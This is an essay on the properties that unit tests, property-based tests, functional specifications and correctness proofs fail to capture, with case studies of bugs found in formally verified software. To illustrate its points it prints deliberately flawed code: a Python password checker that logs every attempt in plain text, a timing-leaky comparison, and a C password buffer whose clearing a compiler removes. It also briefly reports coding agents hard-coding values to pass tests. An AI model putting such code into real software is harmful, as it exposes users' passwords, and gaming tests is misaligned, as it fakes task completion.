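# Software properties that tests and functional specifications fail to capture

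## What tests and functional specifications check

Software testing means running a program on chosen inputs and comparing the results with what its developers want. A functional specification states which outputs or final states a program must produce for which inputs. Both cover what a program computes. They usually leave out how long it takes, which files and servers it touches, whose code it relies on, and whether people will be able to change it safely later. Developers have traditionally caught some of these problems by reading one another's code before accepting it. AI systems now write a large share of new code, more than people can comfortably read, and some developers propose reviewing only the specification and the tests. How far that can work depends on what tests and specifications cover, which a very small program can illustrate.

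### Three tests and a specification

A function is a named piece of a program that takes inputs and returns an output. The one below, in the programming language Python, takes a stored password and whatever somebody has just typed, and returns `True` if the two match. (Real login systems store a scrambled form of the password, which makes no difference here.)

```python
def check_password(stored, attempt):
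    return stored == attempt
```

A unit test runs one such piece of code on one example and compares the output with an answer that the developer wrote down beforehand. *Property-based testing for Spark Streaming* (2018) describes classical unit testing in these terms, as pairs of inputs and expected outputs. Three unit tests for the password function might be:

```python
assert check_password("tulip42", "tulip42") == True
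assert check_password("tulip42", "tulip43") == False
assert check_password("tulip42", "") == False
```

A program's test suite is its full collection of tests. If a suite has three tests for a function that takes two strings, a developer who sees it pass knows the function's output for only three pairs of strings. There are about 218 trillion strings of eight letters and digits, counting upper and lower case separately, and either input could be any of them.

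A property-based test replaces the single example with a general rule and leaves the choice of examples to the computer. It has two working parts, as Naziri, Qin and colleagues (2026), in *A Multi-Domain Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs at Writing Property-Based Tests*, explain: a generator, which draws inputs, and an oracle, which decides for each input whether the program's output is acceptable. For a program *f* with possible inputs *X*, the test approximates the statement

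∀*x* ∈ *X*: pre(*x*) ⇒ *P*(*x*, *f*(*x*))

The formula means that for every input *x* the program is supposed to accept, the property *P* holds between *x* and the output. Two properties are enough for the password function. For any string *s*, `check_password(s, s)` is `True`, and for any two different strings *s* and *t*, `check_password(s, t)` is `False`. The test only approximates the formula because it tries a sample of inputs. Hypothesis, a Python library for such tests, draws 100 inputs by default. When one of them violates the property, it looks for a smaller input that also does, to give the developer a short counterexample.

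The functional specification is that `check_password(stored, attempt)` returns `True` when the two strings have the same characters in the same order, and `False` otherwise. A program has functional correctness when its behaviour agrees with its functional specification on every allowed input, including untested ones. Testing a sample of inputs cannot establish this for a function with so many inputs, but a mathematical proof can. In programs called proof assistants, a developer writes the specification in a formal language, and a small checker confirms each step of the argument that the code meets it. Such proofs used to take a great deal of work. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, gives the example of seL4, the core of an operating system, where proving 8,700 lines of code correct took 20 person-years. AI systems can now write much of such a proof.

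For a function this small, the specification is as long as the code, so reading one instead of the other saves a reviewer nothing, but with larger programs it can. *When AI Writes the World's Software, Who Verifies It?* (De Moura, 2026) describes an AI agent that rewrote zlib, a widely used compression library, in the language Lean and proved that decompressing compressed data returns the original data, at every compression level, for any input under a gibibyte (about a billion bytes). This theorem is a specification much shorter than the code it governs, and a reviewer can judge it without reading that code. It is also partial, because it would hold for a compressor and a decompressor that both return their input unchanged. A reviewer who wants the data to become smaller has to look for that requirement elsewhere.

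### What the tests and the specification leave out

Here is another version of the password function. It passes the three unit tests, has both properties and meets the specification, provided that `textkit.same` compares two strings correctly.

```python
import time, textkit

def check_password(stored, attempt):
    with open("/tmp/attempts.txt", "a") as log:
        log.write(attempt + "\n")
    time.sleep(0.1)
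    return textkit.same(stored, attempt)
```

Few people would want it in a login page. Its faults all lie outside the relation between inputs and output:

- It waits a tenth of a second at every login, for no reason.
- It opens a file and adds each attempted password to it in readable form, including the correct ones.
- It imports a package called `textkit` (an invented name), which is other people's code and may do anything at all when the program loads it.
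- It is harder to understand than the original. A later developer will wonder whether the pause and the log serve some purpose, and may be afraid to remove them.

The one-line original may also have this kind of fault. If the comparison stops at the first wrong character, it takes slightly longer when more of the password's first characters are correct, and an attacker who can measure the time precisely can learn from the difference. De Moura gives a similar example of an AI-written encryption library that passes every test even though one of its branches depends on the secret key.

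### Too few inputs, or a missing property

A program can pass its tests and still be wrong because the tests tried too few inputs. For example, a version of the password function that compares only the last characters of the two strings passes the three unit tests, but it lets in anyone who types `x2`. Random testing will probably expose this bug. If the generator draws twelve-character strings evenly from letters and digits, about one pair in 62 has the same last character, so a run of 100 pairs has about an 80% chance of including one. A version that ignores everything after the eighth character also passes the unit tests, because `tulip42` has only seven characters. Random testing is much less likely to catch this version, since two random strings share their first eight characters about once in 218 trillion pairs. A single test that changes only the last letter of a long password would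 catch it.

AI systems produce errors of this sort too. In *Software Factories And The Agentic Moment*, McCarthy (2026) recalls that his team's coding agent began writing `return true`, which passes a narrow test but does nothing else useful. De Moura reports that a C compiler Anthropic built with AI agents contains hard-coded values whose only purpose is to pass the test suite, and thinks property-based testing would probably catch this. More tests or better-targeted ones catch such failures, although a system that optimises hard against any fixed set of tests may find another gap in them.

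Adding more tests of the same kind does not help if none of them checks the property in question. Naziri and colleagues give the example of a test for a sorting function whose oracle checks that the output list is in order. A sorting function that loses some of the elements passes this test however many inputs are tried, because the remaining elements can still be in order. To catch the error, the developer has to add a rule that the output contain exactly the elements of the input. This rule concerns inputs and outputs, so it fits into an ordinary functional specification. To check a rule that does not fit, such as one against writing passwords to a file, the developer has to watch the file system while the function runs or search the source code for commands that open files.

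Tests can also check properties other than outputs, such as speed. *Harness engineering* (Lopopolo, 2026), an account of a software product written entirely by OpenAI's coding agents, gives the example of an instruction that the service start in under 800 milliseconds. But someone has to think of the property first, and often nobody does. An essay from the consultancy Thoughtworks describes AI-built systems that have every feature their owners asked for but slow down under load or lack security measures that nobody had specified. This is a consultant's impression, without counts, but it is easy to see how tests would miss a requirement that nobody specified. The essay concedes that developers who wrote code by hand seldom considered such requirements at the start either.

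### The proposal to stop reading the code

Google said in April 2026 that AI generated 75% of its new code, up from 25% in October 2024, though human developers still review it, according to The Decoder's *Google says 75 percent of its new code is now written by AI*. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents, AI programs that write code and run commands to finish a task, and 69% agreed that line-by-line review cannot keep up with what the agents produce. The researchers recruited largely through LinkedIn and a paid survey site and did not aim for a representative sample, so the figure suggests only that the worry is widespread.

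One response is to have people review the documents that govern the code instead of the code itself. Ankit Jain, whose company sells infrastructure to teams that work with AI, argues in Latent Space's *How to Kill the Code Review* that people should review "specs, plans, constraints, and acceptance criteria—not 500-line diffs". A diff lists the lines that a change adds and removes. Jain thinks human judgment is most useful before any code exists, when the question is whether the team is solving the right problem. McCarthy's rule is that "Code must not be reviewed by humans". Kleppmann would rely on proof, and compares unread AI code to the machine code that a compiler produces, which almost nobody inspects.

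In *Bootstrapping Coding Agents* (2026), Monperrus, a professor of software technology, describes a small demonstration based on a 926-word specification of a coding agent, which an engineer can read in under five minutes. An existing agent wrote a new agent from the specification, and the new agent then wrote another from the same text. Monperrus checked both by hand and found that they met the specification. He concludes that reviewers should audit the specification, because the code is disposable but any error in the specification will pass into every program that an AI system generates from it.

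Most of these writers want something to replace reading the code. Jain's list includes automatic checks for passwords left in the code, narrow limits on which files an agent may touch, and referral to a human whenever a change affects login code or adds a dependency (outside code that the program relies on). McCarthy keeps many of his test scenarios outside the codebase, where the agent cannot rewrite them to suit its code. According to an essay from the technical publisher O'Reilly, performance, scalability and similar qualities belong in the specification from the start. Martin (2026), a developer, has stopped reading the code in his own projects and uses tests, guardrails and monitoring instead, but he admits in *Human PR Review Is Next* that "It isn't safe to stop reading code".

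Critics doubt that the specification will be easier to read than the code. Haskell for all's *A sufficiently detailed spec is code* (2026) rejects the belief that specification documents are simpler than the code they describe. Thoughtworks' *Where does the rigor go?* mentions a practitioner who would rather review code than specifications, because the code at least reflects what the system does. Kleppmann accepts part of this criticism, saying that once proofs are easy to produce, the hard part becomes knowing whether the proved properties are the ones people cared about.

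The objection is serious for any attempt to specify everything. If a specification has to settle every file name, pause and package, it will grow towards the length of the program and the reviewer gains nothing. If it stays short by leaving those details out, it permits the second password function above. Monperrus recommends sentences that name only inputs, outputs and conditions, and regards a sentence that names a library as probably too detailed, which leaves the choice of packages to the AI system. He also sensibly suggests checking whether the specification describes each error condition and each call to an outside service in the generated code, but somebody or something has to read the code to do that.

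A short specification can still replace reading for one property at a time, where the property allows it. The rest of the case for or against the proposal therefore depends on the answers to four questions about each property:

- Is there a short statement of it? "This function opens no files" is one sentence, however long the function. "This function is easy to understand" is just as short, but two reviewers may disagree about whether a given function satisfies it.
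- Can a machine check it? A tool might run the program, analyse its source text, verify a proof or block the forbidden action outright. Some properties show up in a single run and others only when a tool compares several runs. Some barely show at all. Naziri and colleagues found that even a documented property is hard to test when the program does not display the behaviour in question: to find out how cronie, a program that runs scheduled jobs, had read one line of its settings, a test had to push it past one of its own limits.
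- Under what assumptions does the check hold? The zlib theorem covers inputs under a gibibyte. A random test of the password function is informative only if the generator draws near misses. A speed test that sends identical requests to an empty database, as Thoughtworks points out, reveals very little about a busy service.
- What is left to read? If the operating system denies the password function all access to files, nobody has to search its code for a hidden log. Somebody still has to read the rule that denies the access, and to decide whether `textkit` deserves a place in a login page.

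## Properties of one run, of several runs and of the source text

Software properties fall into three classes: single-run properties, multi-run properties, and properties of the source text and its origin. The class of a property largely determines which checks can work for it. A reviewer can watch a single run of the second password function to learn whether it writes to a file, but has to compare runs with different stored passwords to learn whether its running time gives away the password. The reviewer cannot learn from any number of runs whether a later developer could understand the code.

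### Single-run properties

A trace is the record of one run of a program, as a sequence of states *s*₀*s*₁*s*₂… A state can include anything relevant to the question, such as the program's variables, the files it has open or the time on the clock. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, model a system as the set *T* of all traces that it can produce, over every input and every choice left to chance or to the machine. (They make all traces infinite by letting a finished run repeat its last state forever.)

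A trace property *P* is also a set of traces, namely the acceptable ones. A system satisfies it when all of the system's traces are acceptable:

*T* ⊨ *P* if and only if *T* ⊆ *P*

For the rule "this function opens no files", *P* contains every trace in which no file is opened. One run that opens a file breaks the rule, whatever happens in other runs, so the rule is a "single-run property". The rule that a program must not write to the network after reading a file is another example. So is an ordinary functional specification, because one run with a wrong output violates it.

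Single-run properties include two important kinds, safety and liveness. A safety property forbids something bad that shows up after a finite time and that nothing later can undo. Fredrikson, in *Lecture Notes on Information Flow*, gives the example of reading past the end of an array. In symbols, with *m* ≤ *t* meaning that the trace *t* begins with *m*, a property *S* is a safety property if

*t* ∉ *S* ⇒ there is a finite *m* ≤ *t* such that every *t*′ with *m* ≤ *t*′ is also outside *S*.

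A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, such as every request getting an answer. Formally, every finite trace can be continued in a way that satisfies the property. Every trace property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property.

A test can show that a program violates a safety property, but it cannot show that a server will never answer a request, because the answer might come after the tester stops waiting. Testers usually set a time limit instead. "Every request gets an answer within five seconds" is a safety property, and it is stricter than requiring that every request eventually get an answer.

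### Multi-run properties

Some requirements compare runs with each other. Shashank (2026), in *FCP*, gives the example of a shop's checkout function that must never charge less when a customer adds an item. Under the shop's other rules, a $49.99 cart costs $54.98 with shipping, but a $50.00 cart ships free and costs $50.00. Each charge looks right by itself, so the violation appears only when the two are compared.

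To cover such requirements, Clarkson and Schneider define a hyperproperty **H** as a set of sets of traces, or in other words as the set of systems that the requirement allows:

*T* ⊨ **H** if and only if *T* ∈ **H**

Every trace property *P* corresponds to a hyperproperty, the set of all subsets of *P*. Multi-run properties are the hyperproperties that do not correspond to any trace property in this way. Many of them concern secrets. A limit on the mean response time over all runs is also a multi-run property, since a slow run is acceptable if enough other runs are fast.

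The best-known secrecy requirement is noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined for a machine that several users share. Let *w* be a sequence of commands, each labelled with the user who gave it. Let ⟦*w*⟧ᵤ be what user *u* sees after the machine has carried out *w*, and let *p*(*w*) be the same sequence without the commands of a group *G*. The group *G* does not interfere with another group *G*′ if

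⟦*w*⟧ᵤ = ⟦*p*(*w*)⟧ᵤ for every sequence *w* and every user *u* in *G*′.

Members of *G*′ therefore see exactly what they would have seen if *G* had done nothing. Goguen and Meseguer apply the same idea to particular commands. If the commands for creating, changing and deleting a file do not interfere with a user, and the file did not exist at the start, the machine will always report to that user that the file does not exist. The definition assumes that the model includes everything the machine shows to users. It does not cover what users tell each other outside the machine.

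For a program with public and secret inputs, noninterference means that changing only the secrets makes no difference to what an outsider can observe. Programs whose parts run in parallel need a more careful definition, because even two runs with identical inputs can differ. Zdancewic and Myers (2003), in *Observational Determinism for Concurrent Program Security*, use a requirement that Clarkson and Schneider write as

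∀ *t*, *t*′ ∈ *T*: *t*[0] =_L *t*′[0] ⇒ *t* ≈_L *t*′

Here *t*[0] is the first state of *t*, which contains the inputs. The sign =_L means that an outsider cannot tell two states apart, and ≈_L means the same for whole traces. If a program has observational determinism, the public inputs alone determine what an outsider sees. Zdancewic and Myers' version of ≈_L treats a trace that stops early as equivalent to a longer one with the same beginning, so a program that meets their definition may still leak something by failing to finish.

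One run cannot reveal a violation of these requirements. Suppose a program has one secret bit *h* and one output bit, and both are 1 in some run. That run could come from a program that always outputs 1, which leaks nothing, or from one that outputs *h*, which leaks the whole secret. A rule that checks runs one at a time and accepts all harmless programs must accept every run of "always output 0" and "always output 1". Together, these two programs produce all four combinations of secret and output, so the rule would accept every run of every such program, including the one that outputs *h*. Two runs are enough to expose that program if the secret differs between them and the public inputs don't, because the output changes with the secret.

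Noninterference is too strict for the password function, whose answer has to depend on the stored password. A more useful rule allows the function to reveal only that answer. If two runs have the same attempted password and return the same answer, everything else an outsider can observe must also be the same. A comparison that stops at the first wrong character breaks this rule because its running time depends on how many leading characters are correct. Constant-time code is meant to prevent this.

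### Checking two copies side by side

Observational determinism resembles a safety property in that finite evidence can refute it for good, but the evidence is a pair of runs instead of one. Clarkson and Schneider call a hyperproperty *k*-safety if every violation shows up in the finite beginnings of at most *k* runs and no further behaviour can repair it. An ordinary safety property is 1-safety, and observational determinism is 2-safety. As an example with larger *k*, they describe a system that splits a secret into *k* shares and must never output all of them, even across different runs.

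They also prove that a *k*-safety property of a system *S* is equivalent to an ordinary safety property of *S*ᵏ, a combined system that runs *k* copies of *S* in step. A tool that can check only single runs can therefore check a secrecy rule, provided that somebody first builds the combined program. The idea, known as self-composition, goes back to earlier work, including Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk (2004), in *Secure information flow by self composition*. For two copies run one after the other, it looks like this:

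```python
out1 = program(public, secret1)
out2 = program(public, secret2)
assert out1 == out2
```

Proving that the last line never fails, whatever the three inputs, shows that the output does not depend on the secret. A property-based test can check the last line on random inputs. Both methods compare only the contents of the two outputs. If an outsider can also see how long the program takes or which files it opens, the developer has to record and compare these too.

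Monitoring a program in use for leaks is harder than running two copies in a laboratory, because the two runs that together expose a leak may be weeks apart. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2023) describes monitors that store earlier runs and compare each new run with them, and others that keep a growing list of constraints on later runs. Monitoring a single-run property requires neither stored runs nor a list of constraints on later ones.

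### A correct implementation that leaks

Developers often start from a loose specification and make it more definite in steps until a computer can execute it. An implementation refines a specification if it does only what the specification permits, which means that the implementation's set of traces *T*′ is a subset of the specification's set *T*. Refinement preserves single-run properties, because if every trace in *T* is acceptable, so is every trace in *T*′. A developer can therefore prove such a property once, for the specification, and it will hold for every correct implementation.

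Multi-run properties need not survive. Clarkson and Schneider give the example of a system that may output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit *h*. The functional specification amounts to "output 0 or 1". The secrecy policy is that the possible outputs do not depend on the secret. One programmer resolves the choice by always outputting *h*:

| Secret bit | Outputs that the specification permits | Output of the implementation |
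|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 or 1 | 0 |
| 1 | 0 or 1 | 1 |

The implementation meets the functional specification on every run. The specification satisfies the secrecy policy, because it allows both outputs whatever the secret is. But anyone who sees the implementation's output learns the secret.

*The Shadow Knows* (Morgan, 2007) discusses the same problem as the "Refinement Paradox". McIver and Morgan remark that it is not really a paradox, since ordinary refinement does not preserve speed either. A correct implementation keeps the properties that the definition of refinement covers, and developers have to ensure any others separately.

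A program can leak a secret without anyone intending it to. Zdancewic and Myers consider a program that runs three assignments in parallel, which set a public variable to true, to false and to the secret. The variable can end up true or false whatever the secret is, so the program satisfies a policy that only restricts which outcomes are possible. But if each assignment is equally likely to come last, the variable ends up equal to the secret two times out of three. To prevent this, they require programs to fix the order of any two accesses to the same memory location when at least one is a write.

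Clarkson and Schneider show that refinement preserves exactly the subset-closed hyperproperties. If a system satisfies such a hyperproperty, so does every system that has only some of its traces. Observational determinism is subset-closed, because if all pairs of traces in a set look alike to an outsider, so do all pairs in any subset. The policy in the secret-bit example is not subset-closed, because it requires traces that make each output possible for each secret, and a refinement can remove them. Such a policy is also hard to test. If a tester has seen only output 0 with secret 0 and output 1 with secret 1, the other combinations may be possible but not have come up yet.

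The specification in the secret-bit example violates observational determinism, a stricter secrecy rule, because its output can vary while the public inputs stay the same. A reviewer who applied this rule to the specification would have rejected it before anyone wrote the code.

Checking a program against its specification is not enough if the specification leaves out something that outsiders can observe. *Generalized Security-Preserving Refinement for Concurrent Systems* (Sun, Zhao and colleagues, 2025) describes two versions of an operating-system routine that sends a message from one thread (a part of a program that runs in parallel with others) to another. Under the specification, the routine adds the message to the receiver's queue if the security policy allows it and there is room. Both versions do this, but one also tells the sender when the queue is full. A standard refinement proof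 can ignore this return value and compare only the contents of the queues, and both versions then count as correct. But the policy permits information to flow only from sender to receiver, and the version that reports a full queue lets the receiver signal to the sender by emptying its queue or leaving it full.

The insecure version also leaks information through a counter, which it increases before checking the policy and decreases again if the policy forbids the message. The final state is fine, but another thread can read the counter in between. To prevent such leaks, Sun and colleagues match the steps of the implementation with steps of the specification. If an implementation step changes what some thread can observe, the matching specification step must do so too, and the policy must treat both the same way. When they applied the method to ARINC 653, a safety standard for operating systems,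 they found that two hidden channels known from its single-core version also exist in the multicore version. Their model does not include timing.

Others have changed the definition of refinement. Morgan's version tracks the set of secret values that fit everything an attacker has seen so far, and an implementation may never make this set smaller than the specification would. Replacing "output anything" with "output *h*" shrinks the set to a single value, so it no longer counts as a refinement. *Hyperproperty-Preserving Register Specifications (Extended Version)* (2024) uses strong observational refinement for components that other programs call. Under this definition, a replacement component is acceptable only if every program that uses it keeps all the hyperproperties the program had with the original.

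A functional specification can determine whether correct implementations leak secrets, without a separate secrecy rule, if it fixes exactly one sequence of observable events, including their timing, for each combination of inputs. All correct implementations then look identical from outside, and a reviewer can find out whether they leak by checking whether changing a secret changes the specified sequence. For most programs, however, such a specification would be about as long as the code, and it would forbid harmless improvements such as a faster sorting method. It is usually shorter to leave the functional specification loose and add a secrecy rule with a list of what outsiders can observe.

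Self-composition can also find where a specification is loose. Shashank's Formal Context Protocol, a method for checking AI-written work against the original request, searches for two behaviours that both satisfy the specification, are identical up to some moment, receive the same inputs and then produce different outputs. Each pair shows a choice that the specification leaves to whoever writes the code. For instance, the checkout request did not specify how to round half a cent. That choice does not involve secrets, but the same search would also find the choice left open in the secret-bit example.

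### Properties of the text and its origin

The following function behaves exactly like the one-line password function:

```python
def f(a, b):
    return not (a != b)
```

The changed version is harder to understand than the original, and its name doesn't indicate that it has anything to do with passwords. Yet no test or behavioural specification can accept the original and reject the changed version. Clarkson and Schneider point out that every property of sets of traces is, by definition, a hyperproperty. Two programs with the same traces therefore satisfy the same single-run and multi-run properties.

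Code can also differ in origin while behaving the same. One login page might import the package `textkit`, and another might contain a copy of the one function it needs from that package. The two pages may do the same thing today, but if the maintainer of `textkit` publishes a harmful update next month, only the page that imports the package is likely to receive it. Code that behaves the same can also differ in its licence and author. Many of these properties matter because of what will happen to the program later, which traces of the present version do not include.

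Whether two programs have the same traces depends on what the states record. If the states include the time, adding a pause to a program changes its traces. If every state also included the program's source text, readability would technically become a single-run property, but a reviewer would still have to read the text to judge how readable it is.

Some properties of the source text are easy to check by machine, such as whether a file contains the line `import textkit`. Others, such as whether the names in a program are helpful, depend on the judgment of a reader, human or AI.

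### What automatic checkers can decide

It is much harder to find out whether a program ever loads `textkit`, because it might assemble the name while running or load the package only under rare conditions. Automatic tools are limited in how well they can answer such questions about behaviour. Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, concerns properties of the relation between a program's inputs and outputs. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no algorithm can decide correctly for every program whether it has the property.

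An example shows why. Let `q` be any program that needs no input, and consider this function:

```python
def check_password(stored, attempt):
    q()
    return True
```

Suppose a password function runs a program `q` and then, on its last line, accepts any password. It accepts wrong passwords if `q` finishes and accepts nothing if `q` runs forever. A checker that could always determine whether a password function accepts wrong passwords could also determine whether any given program finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can determine this for all programs. The same argument applies to the rule against opening files if the last line opens a file instead, and to secrecy rules if it outputs a secret.

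The theorem does not prevent anyone from proving things about a particular program, and for most useful programs the answer may be easy to find. But it does mean that every automatic checker for a property of behaviour has to give something up:

- Some checkers reject harmless programs. Barthe and colleagues point out that tools which assign secrecy levels to variables reject the program `output := secret; output := 0`, although its final output is always 0. (If an attacker can read the variable between the two steps, the rejection is right.) Their own method of self-composition avoids such false alarms, but no algorithm can always complete the resulting check.
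- Tests can overlook violations.
- Model checkers, tools that explore every state of a system, always reach an answer if the system is finite and they have enough time and memory. For large programs, developers often have to give them a simplified model, and the answer is then about the model.
- Proof assistants need a person or an AI system to find the proof first, and the search may fail.

A sandbox is an environment that blocks a program from every resource the program has not been granted. It can block an attempt to open a file when the attempt occurs, without having to predict whether the program will make one.

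Even where a checker can always reach an answer, a short rule may be expensive to check. In HyperLTL, a formal language for comparing traces, Finkbeiner writes observational determinism in one line:

∀π. ∀π′. (*l*_π ↔ *l*_π′) → **G** (*o*_π ↔ *o*_π′)

The formula means that for any two runs π and π′ with the same public input *l*, the output *o* is the same at every step (**G** stands for "always"). For a finite system, this property takes relatively little computation to check compared with other multi-run properties, but a direct search through two copies of a system with a million states may still have to consider a trillion pairs of states.

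Checking a rule becomes harder still when it mixes "for all runs" with "there is a run". Generalised noninterference, a relative of the policy in the secret-bit example, requires that for any two runs there is a third that combines the secret inputs of one with the public inputs and outputs of the other. Its formula is only slightly longer than the one for observational determinism, but checking it can take memory that grows as a power of the system's size rather than as its logarithm. Each further switch between "for all" and "there is" can add another exponential to the computing resources needed. According to Finkbeiner, no algorithm can decide for every rule of the form "for all runs there is a run" whether any system could satisfy it. In a more expressive language that he describes, even checking a given finite system against a given rule is undecidable.

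## What a proof of functional correctness leaves open

A machine-checked proof of functional correctness is a stronger check than any test suite, but it shows only that one program meets one specification, under a simplified model of the machine that runs it. In more than fifteen years of searching verified software for bugs, people have found very few in the code that the proofs cover, and many more in the surrounding code, in the specifications and in the tools that check the proofs.

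### The seL4 kernel

A kernel is the part of an operating system that controls the hardware and isolates programs from one another. In 2009, the developers of the seL4 kernel finished a proof that its C code does what its specification prescribes "and nothing more" (seL4 Foundation, *seL4 Proofs*). The proof also rules out several common errors that the specification does not mention. For example, code that always behaves as specified cannot write past the end of an array, because the C standard does not define the result.

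Functional correctness alone does not show that seL4 isolates programs from one another. A kernel could correctly implement a specification that lets any program overwrite another's memory. The developers therefore also proved that programs cannot change data without authorisation (integrity), block each other's access to resources (availability) or learn each other's information without authorisation (confidentiality). Integrity can be checked one run at a time, so if the specification guarantees it, any correct implementation does too. Confidentiality is a form of noninterference, which a correct implementation can violate even when its specification satisfies it.

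The security theorems hold only for a properly configured system. Integrity requires that isolated components have no write access to each other. Confidentiality holds between groups of programs that the kernel schedules separately, but not between every pair of threads. The proofs also vary by processor. The seL4 Foundation has announced a confidentiality proof that completes the isolation proof for AArch64, the 64-bit ARM architecture. However, an undated list of seL4's caveats describes a version for Intel-type processors that has a functional correctness proof but no security theorems.

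According to the seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume*, the developers assume that about 340 lines of ARM assembly code and 1,200 lines of start-up code are correct, and review them by hand. They also assume that the hardware works as documented and that no device overwrites the kernel's memory directly. On some processors they no longer have to trust the compiler, because an automatic tool checks the compiled code against the C code.

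The confidentiality proof also assumes that the model of the hardware includes every route by which information can travel. The Foundation says this assumption is false. The model covers what the kernel stores but not how long operations take. Two runs that differ only in timing are identical in the model, so no theorem about the model can distinguish them. Five years after the confidentiality proof, researchers discovered Spectre, an attack that uses a processor's guesses about upcoming instructions to leak secrets through timing. According to *SoK* (2024), a survey of guarantees in software security, Spectre violates the property that the developers had proved. The Foundation would say that the theorem is still valid but never covered timing. Either way, the theorem does not protect a secret on an affected processor. At the seL4 Summit in September 2026, researchers said their work on a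 proof that covers timing was ongoing.

The Foundation reports no functional correctness defects in the roughly 10,000 lines of verified code since 2009. Over the same period, the developers found small defects in every class of unverified code, including the start-up code. This is the project's own account, though the kernel has been in use for over a decade. The developers still run hundreds of tests after every change. Some of these cover verified code, to check whether the specification describes what the developers wanted.

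### Testing verified compilers and servers

CompCert is a C compiler with a proof that the programs it produces behave like their source code. Yang, Chen and colleagues tested it alongside mainstream compilers in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (2011). Their tool, Csmith, generates random C programs. A script compiles each program with several compilers, runs the resulting executables and compares the number each prints at the end. If the numbers differ, at least one compiler is wrong, so nobody has to know the right answer beforehand. This works only if each program has a single correct meaning, so Csmith has to avoid 191 kinds of behaviour that the C standard leaves undefined.

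In three years the researchers reported more than 325 bugs. Every compiler they tested, including CompCert, silently produced wrong code for some valid program, but CompCert's wrong-code bugs were in parts without a proof. After about six CPU-years of testing, they had found no bugs in CompCert's middle stages, where all the other compilers had some. Csmith did not generate programs with floating-point numbers, recursion or several other features, so the result does not cover these. According to *SoK*, others later found two bugs in verified parts of CompCert, one missed because a specification was too weak and the other because a proof relied on a false axiom.

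Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, spent more than eight months searching three verified research prototypes, IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, which keep copies of data on several servers. They read the code and the specifications, and ran the systems while a tool duplicated network packets, interrupted disk writes and produced system errors. They found 16 bugs:

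| Location | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Code and libraries connecting the verified part to the network, disk and memory | 11 | Verdi erased its old snapshot of the data before it had safely written the new one, so a crash in between lost data |
| Specifications | 2 | IronFleet's specification allowed a server to carry out the same request twice |
| Verification tools | 3 | If the prover crashed, IronFleet's build tool reported that the program had passed |
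| Verified protocols for keeping the copies consistent | 0 | |

One of the 11 is a borderline case. Verdi crashed when a server that had fallen more than 500,000 requests behind tried to catch up, because a function generated from verified code ran out of stack memory. The function was logically correct, but the proof did not cover memory use.

IronFleet's code filtered out repeated requests, but its specification did not require this. The researchers showed the gap by changing seven lines to disable the filter, and the altered program still passed verification. IronFleet's developers disagreed that this was a bug, because their definition of correctness did not include carrying out each request exactly once, and they added a comment saying so. The missing guarantee would probably matter to a bank that used the library for payments, because a repeated request could make the same payment twice.

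The zero in the table is informative because the researchers searched specifically for protocol bugs. They counted 12 such bugs in a one-year sample of bug reports from four mature unverified systems. They warn against comparing total bug counts, since the unverified systems have many more features and users.

### A correct compiler and a password left in memory

Even if a program and its compiler both have proofs, the compiled program may lack a protection that the programmer wrote. D’Silva, Payer and Song (2015), in *The Correctness-Security Gap in Compiler Optimization*, give an example in C, shortened here:

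```c
char *getPWHash() {
    char pwd[64];
    char *hash = malloc(41);
    fgets(pwd, sizeof(pwd), stdin);   // read the password
    /* ... compute its hash, a scrambled form ... */
    memset(pwd, 0, sizeof(pwd));      // overwrite the password
    return hash;
}
```

The `memset` line replaces the password with zeros so that it does not stay in memory. But nothing reads `pwd` afterwards, and to save time, compilers routinely delete writes that are never read. Without the line, the function returns the same hash, but the password stays in memory until something else overwrites it. An attacker who can read the memory, perhaps through a flaw elsewhere in the program, may find it.

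Researchers had already proved this optimisation correct, and the proof still holds. It shows that the program computes the same results before and after the deletion. It does not cover what remains in memory once a function has finished with a variable, because the C standard does not specify this. D'Silva and colleagues explain that such proofs model the state of the program but not that of the underlying machine.

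A compiler can cause a similar problem by moving code. Suppose a program loads a secret only if it is running with special privileges. The compiler may load the secret every time and then clear it if the privileges are missing. The variable ends up with the right value, but the secret has been in memory when it should not have been.

Programmers can prevent some of these changes with special functions, such as Microsoft's `SecureZeroMemory`. Switching off all optimisation would also work, but can make a program about five times slower. The requirement that no copy of the password remains in memory when the function returns is short, but checking it takes a more detailed model of the machine and often much more computation. Deng and Namjoshi (2016) showed that an algorithm can efficiently check whether deleting unused writes preserves a program's results. Nobody knows an efficient way to decide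 whether the deletion creates a new leak, even for programs with finitely many states, and no algorithm can decide this for programs in general. Their own algorithm for deleting writes is fast and never creates such a leak, but it sometimes keeps a write it could safely have deleted.

### Flaws from 2025 and 2026

*Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) describes 13 vulnerabilities in two cryptographic libraries, libcrux and hpke-rs. Nine were in unverified code and four in specifications and proofs. Kobeissi's firm, Symbolic Software, audits cryptography and is in an open dispute with Cryspen, the company behind the libraries. However, an advisory in the vulnerability database GCVE credits Kobeissi with first reporting two of the bugs that Cryspen fixed. Symbolic Software (2026), whose posts call Cryspen "CE Labs", says that Cryspen fixed two departures from a signature standard in March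 2026.

Symbolic Software's *On the Promises of ‘High-Assurance’ Cryptography* (2026) describes several bugs in the unverified code that surrounds verified code. In November 2025, Filippo Valsorda reported that libcrux produced different keys and signatures from the same starting value on two ARM machines. The cause was an unverified substitute for a processor instruction that some machines lack. In hpke-rs, a message counter silently returned to zero after about 4.3 billion messages, so the library reused numbers that it should use only once. This reuse can allow an attacker to read messages. Elsewhere in libcrux, a verified decryption function correctly reported an error for a malformed message, but the unverified code that called it crashed.

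kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes how, in April 2026, a Claude agent ran an AI-written Lean version of zlib about 105 million times on generated inputs. The agent found no memory errors in the program's own code, but a 156-byte ZIP file with a declared size of exabytes could crash the archive reader, which had no proofs. The agent also found a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, the C++ code on which every compiled Lean program depends. When a program requested a block of nearly 2⁶⁴ bytes, the runtime added 24 to the size, the sum wrapped around, and the runtime reserved only about 23 bytes.

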